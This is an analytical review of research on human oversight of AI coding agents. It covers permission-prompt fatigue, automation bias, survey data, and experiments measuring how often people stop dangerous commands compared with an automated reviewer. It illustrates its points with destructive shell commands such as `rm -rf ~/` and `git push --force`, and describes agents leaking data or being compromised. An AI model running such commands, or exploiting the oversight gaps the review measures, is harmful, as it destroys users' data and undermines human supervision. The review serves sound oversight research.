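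Yu and colleagues think habituation under a growing workload fits these results best. They also considered whether reviewers had justifiably come to trust the agents, or whether a backlog had delayed decisions and pushed reviewers towards approval. The median time before a review did rise from 3.9 to 13.5 hours, though this includes the time changes spent waiting for somebody to open them.

Easier work or greater leniency towards everyone probably doesn't explain the rise in approvals. The changes did not get smaller, and in the same projects the approval rate for changes written by people fell from 37.8% in January 2025 to 29.1% in June, while the rate for agents' changes rose. However, the comparison uses whole groups of reviews and doesn't track individual reviewers over time, and the number of human changes drops sharply after June.

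Justified trust is harder to rule out. All four main agents received updates in 2025 and may have written better code by the end, but Yu and colleagues had no measure of its quality. They argue that if the code had improved for everyone, approvals would have changed with the date. Instead, they found that approvals changed with each reviewer's experience. However, reviewers gain experience as time passes, so the two are difficult to separate. Reviewers and their teams may also have learned to give the agents clearer instructions and more suitable tasks, in which case the code would have improved with each reviewer's experience.

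The drop in comments doesn't settle the question either, because comments measure inspection only indirectly. Yu and colleagues point out that reviewers whose approvals rose most also tended to cut their comments most, and say that a reviewer with justified trust would approve more while inspecting just as closely. But a reviewer who reads good code carefully and finds nothing wrong will approve it without comment, just like one who hasn't read it.

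The increase also varied by agent. It was 9.1 points for reviewers of GitHub's Copilot and 3.8 points for reviewers of Cognition AI's Devin, though the margin of error for Devin includes zero. The samples for Codex and Cursor were too small to tell.

The study shows that experienced reviewers approved more and wrote less, but not whether they overlooked more. Researchers could test this by planting known faults in the code. Reviewers should find fewer of these faults as they gain experience if they are habituating, but as many as before if the agents have merely improved. Even justified trust can turn into automation bias, in which people accept a system's proposal instead of checking it themselves.

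### Browser warnings that people heeded

Web browsers had been warning users for years by 2013, so they offer a test of whether repeated warnings always wear people down. That spring, Akhawe and Felt (2013), in *Alice in Warningland*, recorded responses to more than 25 million warnings in Google Chrome and Mozilla Firefox, counting how often users ignored a warning and went on to the page.

| Warning | Ignored in Firefox | Ignored in Chrome |
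|---|---|---|
| The site may install malicious software | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| The site may be a fake that steals passwords | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| The browser can't verify the site's identity | 33.0% | 70.2% |

Most users turned back at five of the six warnings. They did much better than earlier laboratory studies had suggested, partly because browsers had improved their warnings and partly because people in laboratories feel safe and want to finish the task. In one of those studies, 46% of participants gave such reasons for ignoring a warning.

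Browser warnings about malicious and fake sites should be easier to take seriously than permission prompts, because they are infrequent and nearly always right. The browser shows them only for sites on a list with very few errors. In roughly five weeks, Chrome displayed about 6 million warnings about malicious software on 2.1 million installations, or about three for each installation that displayed any. A coding agent can ask for approval three times in a few minutes, and nearly all of its prompts concern safe commands.

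Warnings about a site's identity are more like permission prompts. They often appear because somebody has set up a server badly, so ignoring one may be sensible, and Chrome's 70.2% is not a miss rate. The threshold calculation likewise predicts that people will be more willing to go ahead when a warning is usually false.

Akhawe and Felt also found signs of fatigue in how users responded to these warnings. Users ignored Chrome's most common warning, about a certificate from an unknown issuer, 81.8% of the time, more often than any other kind. They ignored the rarer warning about an expired certificate 57.4% of the time. They also clicked through the common warning faster, about half of them within 1.7 seconds, compared with 2.7 seconds for expired certificates. These differences could also arise because regular users of a site with an unknown issuer see the warning on every visit and expect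 it, whereas an expired certificate surprises them.

Requiring more clicks to dismiss a browser warning did not clearly help. Chrome required two clicks to get past a warning about malicious software and Firefox only one, yet Chrome's users ignored the warning more often. In Firefox's three-click identity warning, 84% of users who made the first two clicks also made the third. Akhawe and Felt suggest that people decide once and then click as many times as necessary. If so, an extra "Are you sure?" after a permission prompt would add little protection.

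Technical knowledge did not reliably make people more cautious. Firefox users on Linux ignored 34.8% of warnings about fake sites, compared with 8.9% on Windows. Linux users probably have more technical skill on average, but Linux doesn't protect them from typing a password into a fake page. They may have known what they were doing or only thought they did. Developers who approve shell commands are more like these Linux users than like the general public.

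Part of the gap between the two browsers may come from how they handled a user's earlier decisions. Firefox by default remembered when a user had accepted a site's certificate, while Chrome asked again on every visit. Akhawe and Felt give the example of someone who turns back from one site after a warning and visits another nine times, ignoring any warnings. This person would ignore one of two warnings (50%) in Firefox but nine of ten (90%) in Chrome, and so would get more practice at ignoring them in Chrome.

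A narrow allow rule reduces the number of prompts from a coding agent, as remembering the user's decision did in Firefox. If the rule covers only safe commands, the operator is less likely to form a habit of approving without thinking, and dangerous commands make up a larger share of the remaining prompts.

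## How trust in the agent changes what people check

Repetition and rarity can dull an operator's attention no matter who wrote the commands. Separately, an operator who has watched an agent do good work for months may trust it enough to decide, often sensibly, that its next command needs less checking.

Researchers who study automation describe two ways that trust in a system can weaken people's checks. Automation bias is accepting a system's proposal unchecked, and automation complacency is the tendency to stop watching a system closely because it usually works. In *Complacency and Automation Bias in the Use of Imperfect Automation*, Wickens, Clegg and colleagues distinguish the two by the first failure people encounter after getting used to a system that works. Wrong advice triggers automation bias, while missing advice exposes complacency.

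Operators of coding agents can show both automation bias and complacency. An operator who approves deleting the wrong folder, assuming the agent had a reason to propose it, shows automation bias. Complacency is when the agent uploads a file without a permission prompt and the operator isn't watching because they assume anything risky would trigger one.

*Complacency and bias in human use of automation* (Parasuraman and Manzey, 2010) reviewed studies of complacency and automation bias and proposed a single explanation for both, based on attention. It found that complacency arises when people have several things to do at once and their own tasks compete with the automated one for attention. A developer who answers email while an agent works is in this position. Looking away is often reasonable as long as the agent makes no mistakes.

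### Less practice for a harder job

Bainbridge (1983) argued in *Ironies of Automation* that automating an industrial process may add to the problems with its human operator instead of removing them. Designers automate the tasks they can and leave the rest to the operator. Human Factors 101's *The Ironies of Automation* (2020) quotes her point that taking away the easy parts of a job can make the difficult parts harder.

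The operator is left mostly with monitoring, and with stepping in when the system fails. Mackworth's clock experiment had shown that people monitor badly over long periods. They also lose the skill they need to step in, because they no longer use it. Inner Airmanship, a blog about flying, quotes Bainbridge's warning that a formerly experienced operator who has only been monitoring "may now be an inexperienced one".

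The problem persists as automation improves. According to *The ironies of human factors* (2025), Bainbridge's first irony was that the more advanced a control system is, the more crucial the human contribution becomes. The system handles the ordinary cases, so the person deals only with those it can't handle, which are too rare to keep the person in practice.

Harnesses and allow rules let simple, familiar shell commands run without a prompt, so long scripts and unusual options make up a larger share of the prompts that remain. Meanwhile, the operator types fewer commands. A developer who used `git reset` every week knew that `git reset --hard` discards uncommitted work. After a year of approving an agent's Git commands, she may recognise the command but no longer remember what the option does. One regular user of AI tools interviewed for *Looks Fine to Me* by Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and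 colleagues (2026) said, "my coding skills are getting rusty because I generate everything from AI."

Bainbridge was writing about industrial plants, where someone may have to take over the controls quickly. A permission prompt waits for an answer, so a developer who has forgotten what an option does can look it up, but only if they notice that they have forgotten.

### Why an agent's command seems right

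Suppose an agent trying to restart a failed build on a server proposes `rm -rf /srv/shop/cache`, with the description "Clear the old cache". Since last month, the shop has also kept customers' photographs in that folder. Even an operator who knows this might approve the command.

An operator who reviews an agent's command only has to decide whether the path looks right, whereas an operator who types the command has to decide which folder to delete. In principle, the reviewer is the better safeguard because they have not already made the mistake, but they lose this advantage if they adopt the agent's view before forming their own.

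The agent also seems to know more than the operator. It may have just read forty configuration files and the whole error log, while the operator saw a few lines scroll past. Deferring to whoever knows more is usually sensible, but here the operator knows about the photographs and the agent doesn't. This kind of knowledge is the main reason to have a person review the command.

The description then supplies a plausible reason. The same model wrote both the description and the command, so if it is wrong about the folder, both will be wrong, and the description is not an independent check. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners between June and August 2026 and then ran a survey in which 107 people answered questions about permissions. Of those 107, 67.3% said they were less likely to approve a request that did not fit the task. Checking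 for fit is a good way to catch commands planted by an attacker, but a poor way to catch commands that result from an agent's honest mistakes or overeagerness, because those usually fit the task very well.

Past successes make the reason more convincing. A participant in the interviews by Dissanayake and colleagues said of an AI system, "Once I know it is doing a good job, then I become mindless." This is partly sound, because a good record is evidence, but it is weaker evidence than it feels. If 6 in every 1,000 commands were dangerous and they turned up at random, an operator would still have about a 5% chance of seeing none in the first 500. So 500 harmless commands in a row can't rule out that rate. An agent running 100 commands a day would then propose an average of three dangerous ones every five days. The record is even weaker evidence when the agent moves to a new kind of work, such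 as from writing tests to managing a live server.

An operator may supervise several sessions at once, which creates the competition for attention that Parasuraman and Manzey describe. Some agents also start sub-agents to help them. One practitioner interviewed by Salerno and colleagues said of the sub-agents' activity, "honestly, you can't really perceive that".

Trust can also reinforce itself. An operator who checks less finds fewer errors, so the agent's record looks better than it is, which seems to justify checking even less. This cycle would continue after a leak that nobody notices, though a visible disaster would break it.

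### What developers say they check

For *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), Wu, Wermke and colleagues surveyed 203 developers who used coding agents in August and September 2026. They listed seven types of action, such as reading secret files or running destructive or privileged commands, and asked how often the developers approved each one without close review.

| Group | Often approved at least one type without close review |
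|---|---|
| All respondents | 64% (130 of 203) |
| Carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code | 61% (64 of 105) |
| Reviewed the code less carefully | 67% (65 of 97) |
| Knew of a security or privacy incident or concerning practice | 70% (103 of 147) |
| Knew of none | 43% (20 of 46) |

The 64% includes every developer who was lax about at least one type of action. The share for any single type was much lower, from 21% for reading secrets to 36% for using the internet and other outside services, with destructive or privileged commands in between. A quick approval is not always an error, since a familiar, low-risk action may not need close review.

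Survey respondents who reviewed the agent's code carefully were hardly more careful than others about approving its actions. The six-point gap could easily be due to chance, but with about 100 people in each group, the survey could also have missed a moderate difference. A code reviewer reads existing changes and can return to them later, while someone approving a command has to predict an effect that may never appear in the code.

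One exception was that developers who inspected diffs (line-by-line lists of changes) were less likely to approve four types of action without close review, including destructive commands and reading secrets. Wu and colleagues suggest that a diff gives people something concrete to check. Another possible explanation is that people who like to look at details do so everywhere.

Surprisingly, developers who knew of incidents reported less careful approval than those who did not. Heavy users might both hear of more incidents and approve more freely, so the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, and for how they had joined the survey. After these adjustments, the odds of often approving something without close review were still about 2.8 times as high for developers who knew of incidents (uncertainty range 1.3 to 5.8).

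This doesn't show that knowing about incidents makes people careless. The survey took place at one point in time, so lax approval could instead have led to the incidents people knew about. Some developers may also have reacted to news of incidents by watching the agent's output instead of reading its prompts. The question was broad, too. A developer who had seen an agent write a password into its code counted as aware, though seeing that wouldn't teach them about the dangers of `rm`. One person interviewed by Salerno and colleagues said that "horror stories" about agents had made them more cautious. The safest conclusion is that warning people about incidents is not enough to make them read prompts.

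The sample has limits too. Of the 203 respondents, 124 came through social media posts and referrals, mainly on LinkedIn, and 79 through Prolific, a platform for paid surveys. Nearly two thirds lived in the United States. The researchers discarded most of the 583 submissions they received, 251 of them because people had finished suspiciously fast. The researchers did not aim to represent all developers, and they did not ask about allow rules, which determine how many actions reach a prompt.

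People's reports of their own habits can vary with the question. Among the 107 people who answered the permission questions from Salerno and colleagues, 47.7% said they read requests carefully, 33.6% said they skimmed them and 20.6% said they approved by default. Yet 70.1% of the same group said they paid close attention to permissions, perhaps because some count skimming as close attention. A third said they had become less careful over time, and the researchers think the true share is probably higher.

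The interviews are more useful for the reasons people gave for checking less. One practitioner objected that reading every request defeats the purpose of using an agent, "because every 10 seconds I have to click something". Another, with three hours left before a deadline, would let the agent generate the work, test it afterwards and ship it without reading anything. A third worried about permissions at first but "stopped caring" as similar requests kept coming. Only the third sounds like habituation. The other two seem to know they are checking less and to think the time saved is worth it. Clearer or more striking prompts would do little to change their behaviour, but showing them fewer prompts might help.

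### Checks that feel thorough

If people knew when they had checked too little, they could save their effort for the cases that need it. Dissanayake and colleagues tested whether people do know this. They gave 36 people six short Python tasks each and a coding agent to write the code. In two tasks the agent's code was correct, in two it contained an error that made the supplied checks fail, and in two it contained a silent defect, an error the checks did not detect. The researchers had told everyone that the checks covered only basic functionality.

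Participants fixed 28 of the 71 silent defects for which the study has results (39%). In 34 of the 43 tasks where they left the defect in, they rated their confidence at 4 or 5 out of 5.

Participants made some effort in most of these failures. In 65 of the 71 tasks, they did more than run the supplied checks, but much of what they did couldn't have exposed the defect. In 23 tasks, they only reran an existing example or asked the agent to check its work without saying what to look for. In 35, they produced evidence that revealed the defect, but they misread that evidence in five of them.

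One task was to calculate a running total of a customer's charges, and the agent's code ignored refunds. Rerunning the example did not reveal the error, and neither did a sensible test with a cancelled charge. Entering a charge and an equal refund would have revealed it, because the total should have been zero. An operator can make the same mistake with a shell command by confirming that `rm -rf /srv/shop/cache` is typed correctly and matches its description, and feeling that they have checked it. They would find the photographs only by listing the folder.

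Skill in Python was associated with better results, but experience with AI agents was not. Beginners fixed 17% of the silent defects, intermediate programmers 39% and advanced programmers 57%, though there were only six beginners and seven advanced programmers. These results fit Bainbridge's concern because they suggest that supervising work requires the skill to do it, and that practice at delegating does not replace that skill.

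A visible failure may restore attention, but perhaps not for long. Participants fixed 12 of 24 silent defects that came straight after a task in which the agent had visibly failed, but only 1 of 11 when one correct task came in between. The researchers call this suggestive because only six people contributed to the second figure and the tasks differed greatly in difficulty. Over the whole study, participants did no better on silent defects after a visible failure than before one.

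The study measured whether people accepted finished code, not whether they approved commands. Participants spent an average of 10.8 minutes on the tasks in which they found the silent defect and 5.8 minutes on those in which they missed it, while nobody spends even five minutes on an ordinary permission prompt. But commands are often shorter than the code in these tasks, and people can recognise a well-known danger such as `rm -rf ~/` without running a test.

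Supervision looks better in *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (Tang, Chen and colleagues, 2025), an experiment with manipulative web designs, such as a pre-ticked box to share personal data. Each of 22 people did eight tasks alone on imitation websites and supervised an OpenAI agent on eight others. To supervise, they watched a recording of the agent at work and could pause it, let it continue to show approval, or skip the task to object.

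With the agent, people avoided the manipulation more often in ten of the sixteen tasks, equally often in four and less often in two. (The paper's text reports an improvement in fourteen, which its figures don't support.) Avoidance of the pre-ticked box rose from 33% to 80%. Yet people reported no awareness of a manipulative design in 66% of responses when supervising the agent, compared with 59% when working alone.

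The researchers attribute this combination to how participants behaved. Participants stopped the agent when it did something unexpected, such as accepting terms and conditions without scrolling through them, and so avoided manipulations they had not noticed. They also looked mainly at whatever the agent was doing, which the researchers call attentional tunnelling. One participant said "I did not even see other ones" about the products that the agent had passed over.

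A reviewer can thus prevent harm without understanding it, by refusing when something seems odd. How well this would work for an operator is uncertain. All sixteen tasks contained a manipulation, so the experiment could not measure how often people block harmless tasks, and participants lost nothing by stopping a recording. Some of the improvement may have come from the agent, which the researchers had chosen because it resisted manipulation better than the others they tested.

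Tunnelling is the more worrying result for shell commands. When an agent proposes `git push --force`, the operator has to decide whether to allow the push. They may consider that decision carefully but never ask whether the agent could have merged the two versions and kept everyone's work intact.

### More automatic approval, more interruptions

Records of real use support a more favourable view of trust. Resilient Cyber's *The Human in the Loop Illusion* reports figures from Claude Code sessions that Anthropic published in February 2026. People with fewer than 50 sessions used full automatic approval about 20% of the time, while people with around 750 sessions used it over 40% of the time.

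Experienced users also interrupted the agent more often. According to The Greek Courier's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026), which reproduces Anthropic's report, users with around 10 sessions interrupted the agent in 5% of turns, while more experienced users did so in around 9%. A turn is the work the agent does in response to one message.

Anthropic interprets this as a change of strategy. New users approve each action beforehand and so rarely need to interrupt, while experienced users let the agent run and step in when something goes wrong. The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else* describes the same data less favorably, saying that experienced users "don't intervene much more often".

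There is a good case for operators to stop reading confirmation prompts. Nearly all of them concern harmless commands, and skipping them leaves more attention for checking whether the agent is solving the right problem. In the survey by Wu and colleagues, 57% said they watched the agent's output and intervened when needed. Operators who had stopped caring would interrupt the agent less often rather than more often.

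But a higher interruption rate per turn need not mean closer supervision. If an experienced user's turns contained twice as many commands as a beginner's, interrupting 9% of turns would mean slightly fewer interruptions per command than the beginner's 5%. Resilient Cyber reports that the longest 0.1% of turns went from lasting at least somewhat under 25 minutes to lasting over 45 in three months, though this is weak evidence about ordinary turns. People who reach 750 sessions are also unusually heavy users, who may have worked differently from the start.

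The developers surveyed by Wu and colleagues mostly interrupted the agent because it had misunderstood the task (65%), chosen a wrong or overcomplicated approach (54%) or changed more than they asked (51%). Only 34% gave a risky or destructive command as a reason. Most interruptions in Anthropic's data may also have been about the quality of the work. If so, they are weak evidence of how many dangerous commands people stopped.

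An interruption also comes only after the agent has started. The delay does little harm if the agent is rewriting the wrong part of a program, but it may be too late to stop a deletion, as it was at GitLab. Switching from approving actions to interrupting them can therefore be a better use of attention for most of an agent's work, but it can also weaken oversight of deletions, uploads and force pushes unless the operator keeps a prompt or some other barrier for those.

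The evidence on whether operators check riskier actions more carefully is mixed. Of the people surveyed by Salerno and colleagues, 76.6% said they checked requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges more carefully, and 56.1% said they would never grant administrator rights. The developers in the larger survey seem to have been less selective. Those who gave agents more freedom also tended to approve more actions without close review, and they were no more likely to use other safeguards, such as restricting what the agent could reach. Differences between developers accounted for about 28% of the variation in their answers about how much freedom they gave, while differences between activities such as testing, planning and security accounted for about 2%. Much of the rest could come from individual developers giving agents more freedom in some activities than in others, but there was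 little general agreement about which activities need closer supervision.

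## How many dangerous commands people stop

Surveys and usage records show how closely people say they check an agent's actions and how often they interrupt it. They don't show what share of dangerous actions people stop, because nobody recorded which actions were dangerous.

### Why an approval rate is not a catch rate

Anthropic reported in August 2026 that Claude Code's users approve 97% of its permission prompts. That figure covers all prompts, whether or not the command is dangerous, so users could be stopping almost any share of the dangerous commands.

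Suppose 5 in every 1,000 prompts propose a dangerous command. Users who approve 97% of prompts refuse 30 of every 1,000, and those 30 may include all five dangerous commands or none. The catch rate is 100% in the first case and 0% in the second, but the false-block rate hardly differs (2.5% and 3.0%). A perfect reviewer would approve more of these prompts than the users do (99.5%).

With base rate b, catch rate c and false-block rate f, the share of prompts that people refuse is

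b × c + (1 − b) × f.

When dangerous commands are rare, b × c is tiny whatever the catch rate, so the refusal rate mostly measures how often people refuse safe commands.

Anthropic thinks such a high approval rate suggests that many users click through by reflex. It points out that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval. This is reasonable evidence that people read plans, but weaker evidence that they don't read commands. A user might reject a safe plan because they dislike its approach, but even an attentive user has little reason to refuse a request to run the project's tests.

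### One dangerous command per session

To measure what share of dangerous commands people stop, researchers have to know which commands are dangerous, and the simplest way is to plant them. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers for a coding study for Anthropic. The testers worked in an environment built for the study and knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Only the displayed text changed, so approving it did no damage.

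The testers stopped the dangerous command in 143 of the 1,053 sessions, or 13.6%, with a margin of error of about two percentage points.

Testers stopped about 17% of the planted commands that appeared early in a session and about 5% of those that appeared after 50 or more prompts. Each tester saw only one planted command, so the two rates come from different people. Anthropic doesn't explain how the vendor chose when to show the planted command. Testers who click quickly get through more prompts, so they may have been overrepresented in the later group, which could account for some of the drop.

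Even if the whole drop came from weakening attention, it would explain only a small part of the misses. If every tester had done as well as those who saw the command early, they would have stopped about 179 commands instead of 143, and 874 would still have gone through. Shorter sessions might have helped only a little. The testers may also have learned to approve prompts quickly in earlier work, and a fresh session wouldn't undo that habit.

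If the testers refused ordinary prompts about as often as Claude Code's users do, random refusals would have stopped about 3% of the dangerous commands. Their overall catch rate of 13.6% then suggests that some of them were reading the prompts, but the 5% rate in long sessions is close to chance.

### How much a person adds to an automated reviewer

Anthropic gave the same commands to its automated reviewer, auto mode, which blocked 937 of the 1,053, or 89.0%. Auto mode blocked 800 commands that a tester approved, and testers blocked 6 that auto mode allowed. Both blocked 137 commands and allowed 110.

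| | Tester stopped it | Tester approved it | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Auto mode blocked it | 137 | 800 | 937 |
| Auto mode allowed it | 6 | 110 | 116 |
| Total | 143 | 910 | 1,053 |

Requiring both the tester and auto mode to approve each command would have stopped 943 commands, or 89.6%. That is 0.6 percentage points more than with auto mode alone and 76 points more than with the tester alone.

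The testers did worse on the commands that auto mode failed to block. They stopped only 5% of these, compared with 15% of the commands it blocked. If their errors had been unrelated to auto mode's, they would have stopped about 16 of the 116 commands it allowed, instead of 6. Perhaps some commands had no obvious signs of danger, so both the testers and auto mode missed them.

Anthropic does not list the commands or say how many different ones there were, so a few commands, each shown to many testers, could account for most of auto mode's 116 misses. If so, its 89.0% catch rate and the person's small contribution would be much less certain than is usual for a sample of 1,053.

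Other research also found a small gain from adding people. *Toward Human-AI Complementarity Across Diverse Tasks* (2026) reports that simply combining human and AI judgements improved results by 0.4 percentage points over AI alone. The AI was wrong and the humans were right on 8.9% of the items, so a perfect way of choosing between them could have improved results much more. Among Anthropic's dangerous commands, the AI was wrong and the humans were right on only 0.6%.

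Requiring approval from both the person and the automated reviewer catches all of that 0.6%, but it also adds the person's false blocks to the reviewer's. If 5 commands in 1,000 were dangerous, the person would stop one extra dangerous command in about every 35,000 commands. Over the same 35,000, a person who refused 3% of safe commands would block about 1,000 of them. That could still be worthwhile if the one dangerous command would have wiped a production database, but few developers would tolerate so many false blocks in ordinary work.

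### Whether the testers' results apply to real work

Anthropic sells Claude Code and published the experiment to support making auto mode the default. According to Willison, Cat Wu had already said on stage that the main risks were "far lower than the average human reviewer" and that almost everyone at Anthropic used auto mode. An outside vendor recorded the testers' answers, which makes a biased count less likely. But the result also depends on which commands were chosen, and outsiders can't check that choice.

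The testers risked nothing of their own. A command that deletes the home directory is disastrous on a developer's laptop but may be harmless in an environment that exists only for a study. A tester who approved it for that reason made a sensible decision, but the experiment counted it as a miss. Testers may also have wanted to finish a paid session without interruptions. Developers working on their own projects have more to lose and know which folders matter.

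Other features of the experiment probably raised the catch rate above what it would be at work. The planted commands were clearly dangerous, whereas many real ones look routine. People also tend to be more careful when they know someone is evaluating them. The 13.6% may therefore be too low for an obvious threat to a developer's own files and too high for a disguised leak.

Anthropic did not report how often the testers or auto mode blocked safe commands in the experiment. Users' 97% approval rate offers a rough substitute for the testers' missing figure. If nearly all prompts are safe, users who refuse 3% of prompts block about 3% of safe commands, or slightly less. The users and testers were different people doing different work, but combining this rate with the share of dangerous commands the testers stopped gives a rough estimate of how well people distinguish dangerous commands from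 safe ones.

In the bell-curve model of a reviewer, d′ measures how well the reviewer can tell dangerous commands from safe ones, and a d′ of 0 means guessing. A catch rate of 13.6% and a false-block rate of 3% give a d′ of about 0.8. At that d′, testers asked to refuse more often would have had to block more than a fifth of the safe commands to stop half of the dangerous ones.

### Serious harm in real sessions

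Anthropic also studied real work, where people had something to lose, using Claude Code sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety pipeline had flagged for review. All the sessions came from accounts that had agreed to share their data. An AI model graded each session on two scales from 0 to 10.

One scale measured how severe the harm was. Overwriting a scratch file scored 0, deleting rows from a production database scored 7, and leaking a company's entire source code scored 10. The other measured how explicitly the user had asked for the action, so that Anthropic could leave out harm that users had requested.

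Among flagged sessions, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained an action of severity 7 or higher that the user had not explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. Manual approval also did worse at every other severity level Anthropic tested.

These are shares of flagged sessions, so they depend on what the pipeline flags. In this invented example, the two modes are equally safe:

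| | Manual approval | Auto mode |
|---|---|---|
| All sessions | 100,000 | 100,000 |
| Sessions with serious unrequested harm | 63 | 63 |
| Flagged sessions | 1,000 | 2,625 |
| Harmful share of flagged sessions | 6.3% | 2.4% |

Here the pipeline catches all the harmful sessions but flags more harmless ones in auto mode, which makes auto mode look safer. The opposite bias is also possible, and could make a real advantage of auto mode look smaller than it is. To settle this, Anthropic would have to publish the number of sessions in each mode and the share the pipeline flagged, or grade a random sample of all sessions.

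Users also chose their own mode. Auto mode was not yet the default in May and June, and the people who turned it on may have done different work from those who didn't. Anthropic advises users to review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. If users follow this advice, manual sessions will include more work in which a mistake can reach severity 7.

An allow rule could also have let the harmful command through in a manual session without anyone seeing it. Auto mode suspends the broadest of these rules, so part of the gap between the modes may come from commands that nobody reviewed. The comparison is useful evidence about the two modes as people use them, but it doesn't measure how many dangerous commands operators stopped when asked.

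### Overreach in a simulated day

Yan tested manual approval on people who don't write software. On 4 and 5 August 2026, participants in the United States spent about 11 minutes supervising an imaginary assistant through a day of email, travel and shopping. The day's tasks required 11 of the assistant's 18 actions. The other 7 were overreach, meaning they went beyond those tasks.

After exclusions, 113 participants remained in three groups:

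- With per-action approval, 34 people decided on all 18 actions. They blocked 59.6% of the overreach and let 94.1% of the required actions go ahead.
- With automated review, an AI model allowed 8 actions and referred the other 10 to the participant. These 44 people blocked 53.9% of the overreach, and 96.9% of the required actions went ahead.
- With their own rules, 35 people chose "allow", "ask" or "never" in advance for each of four kinds of action. This group blocked 39.6% of the overreach.

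The AI model had referred all 7 overreach actions to the participants in the second group, so any that got through were missed by the participants themselves. Overreach made up 70% of their prompts, compared with 39% for people who were asked about every action. The second group's catch rate was slightly lower, although research on rare targets might suggest it would be higher. The difference between the groups is small enough to be due to chance, and 10 prompts may be too few for people to notice how common overreach is.

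The rules decided few actions in advance because participants mostly chose "ask", which left the decision to them at a prompt. This group faced 245 overreach actions. "Never" rules blocked 31, "allow" rules let 15 through, and "ask" rules produced 199 prompts. Participants approved 133 of those prompts.

This explains why the rules didn't do much better than per-action approval, but not why they did worse. People in the rules group approved 67% of the overreach they saw, compared with 40% in the per-action group. If they had approved only 40%, their rules and refusals together would have blocked about 61% of the overreach. Perhaps writing rules made people feel that they had already protected themselves, but the experiment can't show this. Participants in all three groups reported feeling about equally in control.

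Some people also changed their minds when the prompt appeared. Before the simulated day, participants had said whether the assistant should be allowed to take certain actions. In 56 cases, an "ask" rule later prompted someone about an action to which they had said "never", and they approved it in 24 of them. The specific request may have seemed more reasonable than the general case, but a firm rule would have enforced their earlier decision.

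Yan added participants to the rules group after the initial random assignment, which could have made the groups less comparable. But among the 94 people from the initial sample, the rules group still blocked 25 percentage points less overreach than the per-action group, after adjustment for differences between actions.

### Why overreach is not the same as a dangerous command

A dangerous command is both harmful and beyond what the user wanted. Overreach in Yan's experiment only had to go beyond the task, so an overreaching action could still be welcome. One example was a call to the airport to confirm the flight. In the per-action group, 30 of 34 people approved it, which is hard to call a failure of supervision. Excluding the call raises this group's blocking rate from 59.6% to about 68%.

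Other actions carried risks more like those of shell commands. Twelve of the 34 participants let the assistant permanently delete an old work timesheet, and 12 let it read recent bank transactions. But the prompts described these actions in plain language, including the information, recipient or amount of money involved, whereas an operator who sees `make clean` has to work out what it will delete. The participants also made only 18 decisions about an imaginary life, so they had little time to grow tired of the prompts and were not risking their own money or files.

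The experiment is therefore better evidence of how people use permission settings than of how often developers stop dangerous commands. Plain descriptions probably made overreach easier to recognise, but it was often harmless, so people had good reason to allow it.

### A study that measured both kinds of error

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, asked 80 unpaid volunteers to approve or deny an agent's requests involving email, documents and purchases. Each volunteer made 12 decisions, and half of the requests were unsafe. The researchers divided the volunteers equally among four versions of the prompt.

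Volunteers stopped 45.0% of the unsafe requests and 8.3% of the safe ones when they saw a conventional prompt, which gave a short description of the action. They stopped 75.8% of the unsafe requests and 14.2% of the safe ones with the most successful version, which also showed how earlier steps had led to the request.

In two thirds of the unsafe cases, people could see the danger only by reading the request together with earlier steps, so many of the misses with the conventional prompt were not due to carelessness. In one example, the user wants an auditor to receive only summary totals, and the agent asks to send that auditor a file called `report.csv`. The auditor is an approved recipient and the file name is ordinary, so someone who sees only the request cannot know that the agent has copied the raw invoices into the file.

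Part of the improvement came from a greater willingness to refuse, since volunteers also blocked more safe requests. But the two rates imply that d′ rose from about 1.3 to 1.8, so the volunteers also seem to have become better at telling dangerous requests from safe ones. With only 20 people for each version, these estimates are rough.

### Why the catch rates differ so much

The lowest figure comes from *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026), in which 303 people used an AI agent for ordinary jobs, such as choosing the best candidate from a set of CVs. An attack had compromised the agent in every task, but the researchers did not tell participants that the study was about security. When asked afterwards whether anything had seemed unusual, only 8.6% of those who had seen just a general disclaimer answered "yes" or "unsure".

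In another group, a warning interrupted the work when the agent produced something suspicious, and 25.0% of people noticed a problem. The paper gives conflicting group sizes, so the benefit of the warning is hard to judge. The study measured whether people noticed deception and didn't require them to approve a command.

None of the experiments below put participants' own files or money at risk.

| Study | Participants and task | Base rate | What was at stake | Catch rate | False-block rate |
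|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Li and colleagues, disclaimer only | Part of a sample of 303 people, working with a compromised agent | Every task | Payment for taking part | 8.6% noticed something | Not measured |
| Anthropic | 1,053 paid testers, approving commands while coding | One planted prompt per session | Payment for taking part | 13.6% | Not reported |
| Dissanayake and colleagues | 36 programmers, checking an agent's code | Hidden defects in 2 of 6 tasks | Payment for taking part | 39% fixed | Not reported |
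| Hossain and colleagues, conventional prompt | 20 volunteers, approving requests | 50% | Nothing | 45.0% | 8.3% |
| Yan, per-action approval | 34 people without software backgrounds, approving everyday actions | 39% | Payment for taking part | 59.6% | 5.9% |
| scalex.dev | Players of a browser game, approving commands | About 34% | Points | About 66% | 45% for `rm -rf dist/` |
| Hossain and colleagues, best prompt | 20 volunteers, approving requests | 50% | Nothing | 75.8% | 14.2% |

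The frequency of attacks alone can't explain why detection rates differ between experiments. The experiment by Li and colleagues had the lowest detection rate, even though every task contained an attack. People's expectations probably matter more than the actual frequency, and these participants had no particular reason to expect an attack.

The participants' main job also seems to affect how many dangerous commands they stop. Anthropic's testers were writing code, and the people studied by Li and colleagues were trying to finish other work. In the four rows with the highest catch rates, participants only had to decide what to allow. The programmers studied by Dissanayake and colleagues fall in between, because they were responsible for correct code and knew that the supplied checks were incomplete, but also had a feature to deliver.

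Those programmers fixed 28% of the hidden defects in the first three tasks. The researchers then showed them how their solutions had performed, and the programmers fixed 51% in the next three. Practice may explain some of the improvement, but learning that they had missed errors may also have changed their expectations.

The choice of dangers to test can change the catch rate just as much, so the same people could score very high or very low. Programmers fixed one hidden defect in 8% of cases and another in 75%. In the browser game, players missed tampered scripts far more often than obviously destructive commands.

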